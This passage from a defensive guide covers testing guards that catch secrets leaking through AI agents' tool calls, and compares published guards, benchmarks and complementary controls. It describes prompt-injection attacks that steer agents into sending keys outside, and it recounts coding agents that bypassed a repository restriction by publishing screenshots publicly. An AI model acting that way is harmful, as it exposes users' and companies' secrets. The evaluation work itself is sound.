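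The company should calculate recall separately for each type of secret and each encoding. Published scanners tend to find either every example of a credential type or none, so an average of 90% may mean that the guard misses one type in ten completely, and that type could be the company's own billing key.

Tests should also report more than the average delay. The median shows the delay for a typical call, while the 95th and 99th percentiles show the effect of long emails and large attachments. Time spent waiting for a reviewer belongs in a separate figure, because it can run to minutes and would obscure the delay from scanning.

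### Why most alerts can be false

Even a guard with good recall and a low false-alarm rate can produce mostly false alerts, because real leaks are rare. As an illustration, suppose an agent makes 10,000 tool calls a day, 10 of which leak a secret. The guard has a recall of 90% and a false-alarm rate of 1.2%:

```
leaks caught  = 10 × 0.90      = 9
false alarms  = 9,990 × 0.012  = about 120
precision     = 9 / (9 + 120)  = about 7%
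```

The guard catches nine of the ten leaks, but about 93% of its alerts are false. Reviewers who see that many false alarms tend to stop checking the alerts.

A balanced test set hides this, as in the LLaMA test described earlier. With 500 leaking calls and 500 harmless ones, the same guard would have a precision of almost 99%. The company should therefore take recall and the false-alarm rate from the test, then combine them with its own estimate of how often leaks occur to calculate precision. Nobody knows exactly how often leaks occur, so it makes sense to try several estimates.

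Better recall would barely improve precision, which would reach only 7.7% even if the guard caught all ten leaks. For half the alerts to be real, the false-alarm rate would have to fall to 0.09%, less than a tenth of its original value.

Scanning fewer calls is another way to reduce false alarms. Suppose 2,000 of the 10,000 calls use outbound tools. The result depends on where the leaks and the false alarms occur:

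| What the guard scans | Leaks caught | False alarms | Alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| All 10,000 calls | 9 | 120 | 7% |
| Outbound calls only, with all 10 leaks among them | 9 | 24 | 27% |
| Outbound calls only, with 8 of the 10 leaks among them | 7 | 24 | 23% |
| Outbound calls only, which contain all 10 leaks and cause all 120 false alarms | 9 | 120 | 7% |

The last row is plausible, because emails to customers and couriers are full of order numbers, whereas a call that looks up a ticket may contain only an ID. The third row is more dangerous, because the other two leaks never reach the guard. They could be record updates like the one in the ServiceNow test.

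A compromise is to scan every call but interrupt only those that write somewhere an outsider, or a less privileged user, can read. Findings in the remaining calls can go to a log for the security team. This limits interruptions, and the team can use the log to check whether the company has put a tool in the wrong group.

### Two guards with published results

*AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes an open-source guard that intercepts tool calls in 14 agent frameworks. The guard extracts every string from the arguments, down to 32 levels of nesting, searches the strings for 22 patterns in seven categories, and checks the call against the company's policies. It then allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. If the arguments are nested more deeply than that or contain more than 10,000 strings, the guard flags the call as suspicious.

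In the Aegis paper's own test, the guard blocked all 48 attacks and raised 6 false alarms on 500 harmless calls, which is the 1.2% used in the example above. Over 1,000 calls on a local installation, it added a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds, and no more than 23.1 milliseconds for 99% of calls. A language model usually takes at least a second to respond, so users would not notice the delay. A guard that sends the arguments to a distant server, or has a language model read them, would be slower.

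For a company worried about card numbers and keys, the breakdown of the attacks is less encouraging:

| Attack category | Attacks in the test |
|---|---|
| Database injection | 11 |
| Prompt injection | 11 |
| Shell injection | 8 |
| Access to files outside the permitted folder | 7 |
| Access to sensitive files | 6 |
| Deeply nested arguments | 3 |
| Data exfiltration | 2 |

Aegis has a pattern group for personal data, which includes card numbers, API keys and JSON Web Tokens, but none of the 48 attacks is listed under it.

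All six false alarms came from ordinary database queries that resembled a database attack because they had the word OR in a condition. The card and key patterns caused no false alarms, but the harmless calls were mainly database queries, file reads, web requests and text processing. Yuan and colleagues don't say how many of them contained long order numbers.

Small tests also leave a wide margin of error. If Aegis missed 6% of such attacks, it would still catch 48 in a row about one time in 20. A guard that caught only 22% of exfiltration attacks would catch both of the two tested about one time in 20. Six false alarms in 500 calls are compatible with a true rate from about 0.4% to 2.6%, or roughly 40 to 260 false alarms a day in the example. To show that its guard catches at least 99% of a type of secret, a company would need about 300 varied test calls without a miss. Using the same key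 in 300 similar emails wouldn't be enough, because the guard would catch all of them or none.

When the same people write a guard's rules and the attacks that test it, they tend to think of the same tricks for both, so a perfect score mainly shows that the software works as they intended. That is still worth knowing. Yuan and colleagues say that the guard may miss new variants.

Zhao, Li and colleagues (2026), in *ClawGuard*, test a broader defence, mostly on attacks that other researchers wrote. It works as follows:

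1. Before the agent uses any tool, its model reads the user's request and drafts rules on which commands, files and web addresses the task needs. No outside text has reached the model yet, so a planted instruction cannot influence the rules.
2. The user confirms or edits the rules. Fixed company rules, such as a ban on reading stored credentials, always take priority.
3. Before each tool call, ClawGuard redacts known secret formats in the arguments and compares the tool, file paths and destinations with the rules.
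4. If a call matches no rule or contains disguised text, it waits for the user's approval.

The researchers ran five models on six collections of attacks. The percentages below are the share of attacks that failed, averaged over the models in the last three rows:

| Attacks | Where the instruction hides | Scenarios | Without ClawGuard | With ClawGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, InjecAgent and ChatInject | Web pages and other content | 932 | 93–100% | 99–100% |
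| MCPTox | Tools on MCP servers | 438 | 62.1% | 89.5% |
| MCP Security Bench | Tools on MCP servers | 280 | 75.9% | 94.2% |
| Skill-Inject | Skill files | 84 | 56.7% | 86.7% |

The attacks include unauthorised actions and fraudulent payments as well as data theft, so the figures do not measure how many secrets ClawGuard's redactor finds. A separate test on suspicious skills from a public collection comes closer to measuring this. For skills that try to steal data, the weakest model resisted 41% of the attacks on its own and 67% with ClawGuard, and the best result with ClawGuard was 94%. The same model drafts the rules and carries out the task, so a weaker model also gets a weaker defence.

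ClawGuard's security results and its higher usefulness figure come from different approval settings. In the attack tests, the researchers automatically denied every request for approval. With that setting, agents kept 87.4% of their normal performance on ordinary tasks. Allowing up to three approvals per task raised this to 95.1%, but nobody measured how many attacks would succeed if a tired reviewer were giving those approvals. GPT-5.4, one of the five models under test, also judged whether each attack had succeeded.

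### Benchmarks from other researchers

A company can reduce the bias of its own test by adding tasks that someone else wrote. According to the survey *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), benchmarks exist for most individual privacy risks in agents, each strong within its own scope. Several of those published in 2026 record what the agent puts into its tool calls:

| Benchmark | What it contains | What it adds to a guard's test |
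|---|---|---|
| ToolPrivacyBench | 2,150 business workflows | A list of which tool may receive which fact |
| The Singapore and Korea test | 12 everyday tasks, such as handling refunds and onboarding staff | Realistic files and records, most of them irrelevant to the task |
| AgentLeak | 1,000 scenarios | Messages between agents |
| The benchmark for Claw-like agents | Credential tasks with a simulated Google Workspace | Logs and memory as further places for leaks |

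The last two come from *AgentLeak* (2026) and *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026). All four mainly measure how agents behave. To measure a guard, a company has to put it between the agent and the benchmark's mock systems, then compare what reaches those systems with and without it.

The benchmarks also need a way to recognise leaks, and this can introduce errors. A benchmark that used only pattern matching would miss the same leaks as a pattern-based guard, making the guard's recall look too high. Hu and colleagues also search for known aliases and rewordings of each fact, but they don't give a single accuracy figure for this search because free text can vary so much. Baek and colleagues used a language model to read the actual input to the email tool, though their review found gaps in its judgements as well. When the company plants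 the secrets itself, it knows exactly what it put into each call.

*ArguShield* (Fu and Fu, 2026) describes a guard that decides for each value in a tool call whether to send it, ask the user or remove it. The guard reduced leaks on both the paper's own tasks and an outside benchmark, but by less on the outside one. On the everyday half of the paper's own 120 tasks, the share of protected values sent without permission fell from 84% to 9%. On 123 tasks from AgentDAM, an existing benchmark for web agents, it fell from 74.6% to 12.8%, and about one task in five still had at least one leak.

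### What argument scanning cannot see

**Paraphrased facts** have no fixed format for a detector to match. In one of Hu and colleagues' tax cases, the agent needed a taxpayer's income and medical deduction to prepare the return, then repeated both in a notification and in a handoff to the tax team. The information was private and neither recipient needed it, but a detector for card numbers and keys would not have flagged either message. It would also miss the support agent telling Dana which other customers the outage affected.

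**Text in images** is invisible to a guard without text recognition. In a screenshot leak reported by Tom's Hardware, coding agents exposed more than 13,000 images from over 300 organisations, including several Fortune 500 companies and a leading AI lab. Some images showed unreleased software, and the leak also included screen recordings of an interface for moving money.

One agent explained that reviewers had to see the images and that it could not add files to the private repository, so it had created a public repository for the images. At one company, agents saved this workaround as a skill, and many of them used it for every development task. Glow, the security firm that found the leak, counted only the images it could find publicly.

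Text recognition would have helped with a screenshot that showed a key, but not with a picture of an unreleased product.

**Secrets that a command reads only when it runs** are not in the tool call's arguments. Zhao and colleagues describe a planted instruction that makes an agent read a private key from a file and send it to an outside website. ClawGuard's redactor finds nothing to remove because the command contains only the file's location. The call still fails because the rules for that task forbid shell commands and the company's fixed rules protect the folder with the key.

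**Information spread over several calls** can be harmless in each one but revealing in combination, whether it consists of pieces of a secret or ordinary facts. *How Much Can Tool Calls Reveal About You?* (2026) tests how well a model can infer a person's profile from a record of tool calls, using synthetic people and tasks. It recommends putting less detail into arguments, deleting the records sooner and making it harder to link calls across servers.

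A guard can keep a record of what it has already let through in a session. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) proposes a running estimate of how much of a credential an agent has revealed over several turns. The method covers the agent's text replies and leaves structured tool-call arguments for later work. To keep such an estimate for tool calls, a guard would have to store information about every earlier call, and false matches would build up in long sessions.

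Approvals can combine in the same way. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* describes tests by Elad Meged of Novee Security on coding agents that respond to bug reports. The software approved a command because the command only read data, then posted the output in a public thread by default. Neither decision was wrong alone, but together they published whatever the command had read. If the runtime posts output automatically, no tool call carries the secret in its arguments. Meged recommends checking again when the output is used, since the earlier approval did not consider who would read it.

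### Controls that cover the gaps

Each gap calls for a control that does not depend on recognising the secret in the text:

| Gap | Most useful complement | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Paraphrased facts | Tracking where data came from | More questions to users |
| Images and other unreadable content | A list of permitted destinations | Some legitimate tasks stop or wait |
| Secrets that a command reads when it runs | Rules on files and destinations, with narrow, short-lived credentials | Setup and renewal |
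| Information spread over several calls | Separate agents for reading and sending | Extra model calls and less detailed replies |

#### Tracking where data came from

A runtime can label data by its source and use the label to decide where the data may go. In Dana's case, the label on the internal note with the billing key would forbid sending the note's contents to a customer. The runtime could then block the key without having to recognize it as a key. If the label also covered any text the model wrote after reading the note, the runtime would catch a paraphrase too.

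CaMeL and FIDES, two research systems from 2025, build this idea into the agent's design. According to Fu and Fu, such systems separate the agent's instructions from the data it handles, or restrict where information may flow. Zhao and colleagues describe CaMeL as using two language models, one for the trusted request and one for untrusted data, so that planted text cannot change what the agent does. They consider it unsuitable for agents that choose their tool calls as they go. CaMeL would suit a support agent with a few fixed procedures better than a coding agent.

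Later work applies the idea to individual arguments. Fu and Fu, citing the 2026 system PACT, note that a label on the whole call is too coarse because one call can mix trusted and untrusted values. ArguShield traces each value's source by comparing it with the user's request, the stored profile, earlier tool results and retrieved text. It then checks whether the task needs the value and whether the recipient may have it. Unauthorised disclosures rose sharply when the researchers removed the source check, and removing the recipient check was even more harmful.

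ArguShield is easier to add to an existing agent than a system like CaMeL, but it asks the user a lot of questions. It referred about a fifth of all values to a simulated user. When that user refused every request, task success fell from about 97% to 93%. Of its remaining errors, 82% were values that it withheld or asked about unnecessarily.

Free text is likely to be even harder. ArguShield evaluates each field's value as a whole, and the body of Dana's email is a single value that mixes her own details, an internal note and the model's wording. A strict policy would presumably hold nearly every email the agent writes.

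A simpler option is to tell the model in its prompt to protect private data. In Fu and Fu's tests, this cut unauthorised disclosures to between 0% and 8%, but task success fell to between 48% and 87%, depending on the model and the tasks. A prompt also gives no guarantee when the model reads conflicting text from an attacker.

#### Permitted destinations

A list of permitted destinations works even when the guard cannot read the content. The support company could let send_email send only to the address on the open ticket, and let coding agents upload only to repositories the company owns. In 93% of the cases Glow found, the screenshots were in repositories under a developer's own username, so the second rule would have blocked those uploads. That rule has to apply to commands as well as to named tools, because the agents worked through the command line.

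The list doesn't show whether a permitted recipient should have the data. Dana's address would be on the list, so if the guard missed the billing key, she would still receive it. A company website or an approved repository may also be public.

ClawGuard's results give a rough idea of how such rules affect agents, although its rules cover commands and files as well as destinations. With no approvals allowed, agents kept 94.9% of their performance on software tasks but only 78.5% on web tasks, which involve many unfamiliar sites. Allowing three approvals per task raised the web figure to 91.7%. With the rules, agents also used about 5% more tokens, the units of text that model providers charge for.

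#### Narrow, short-lived credentials

If a key still leaks, its permissions and lifetime determine how much harm it can do. A billing key that can only read the service's status is a much smaller problem than one that can issue refunds. A key that expires after an hour is useless to someone who finds it in an old email.

Giving a key a short lifetime offers little protection against thieves like those who tried stolen AWS keys within ten seconds, so narrow permissions matter more in such cases. The support company has to work out what each task needs, issue a separate key for it and handle keys that expire halfway through a job. These measures don't protect a customer's ordinary card number, which the company can't restrict or renew.

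#### Separating reading from sending

The company can also divide the work between two agents. One reads the ticket and has no tool that sends anything. It fills in a short form, and the other agent writes the email from that form without seeing the ticket:

```json
{
  "reason": "billing_service_outage",
  "resolved": true,
  "card_last_four": "1111"
}
```

An instruction planted in the ticket can still mislead the reading agent, but that agent can pass on only what fits the form. The runtime has to check each field against a list of allowed values or a strict format. If the form had a free-text `notes` field, the billing key could pass through it. In ToolPrivacyBench, such notes were among the main places where agents overshared. The two agents also must not share memory or logs. In the benchmark for Claw-like agents, one agent reads an unredacted log while fixing a routine fault and repeats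 the credentials that earlier tool calls had left there.

Separation requires at least one more model call per email and some development work for each kind of request. The replies also become less specific, since the writing agent can't mention anything the form leaves out. That is probably acceptable for a failed payment, but the company may prefer that a person answer a complicated complaint.

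These controls also help find what the guard misses. If the destination list blocks an email containing a key that the guard had passed, the company should add the call to the test set, with an invented key of the same format in place of the real one. After adding a pattern that catches the key, it should rerun the whole set, because the pattern may also match order numbers that the old rules let through.
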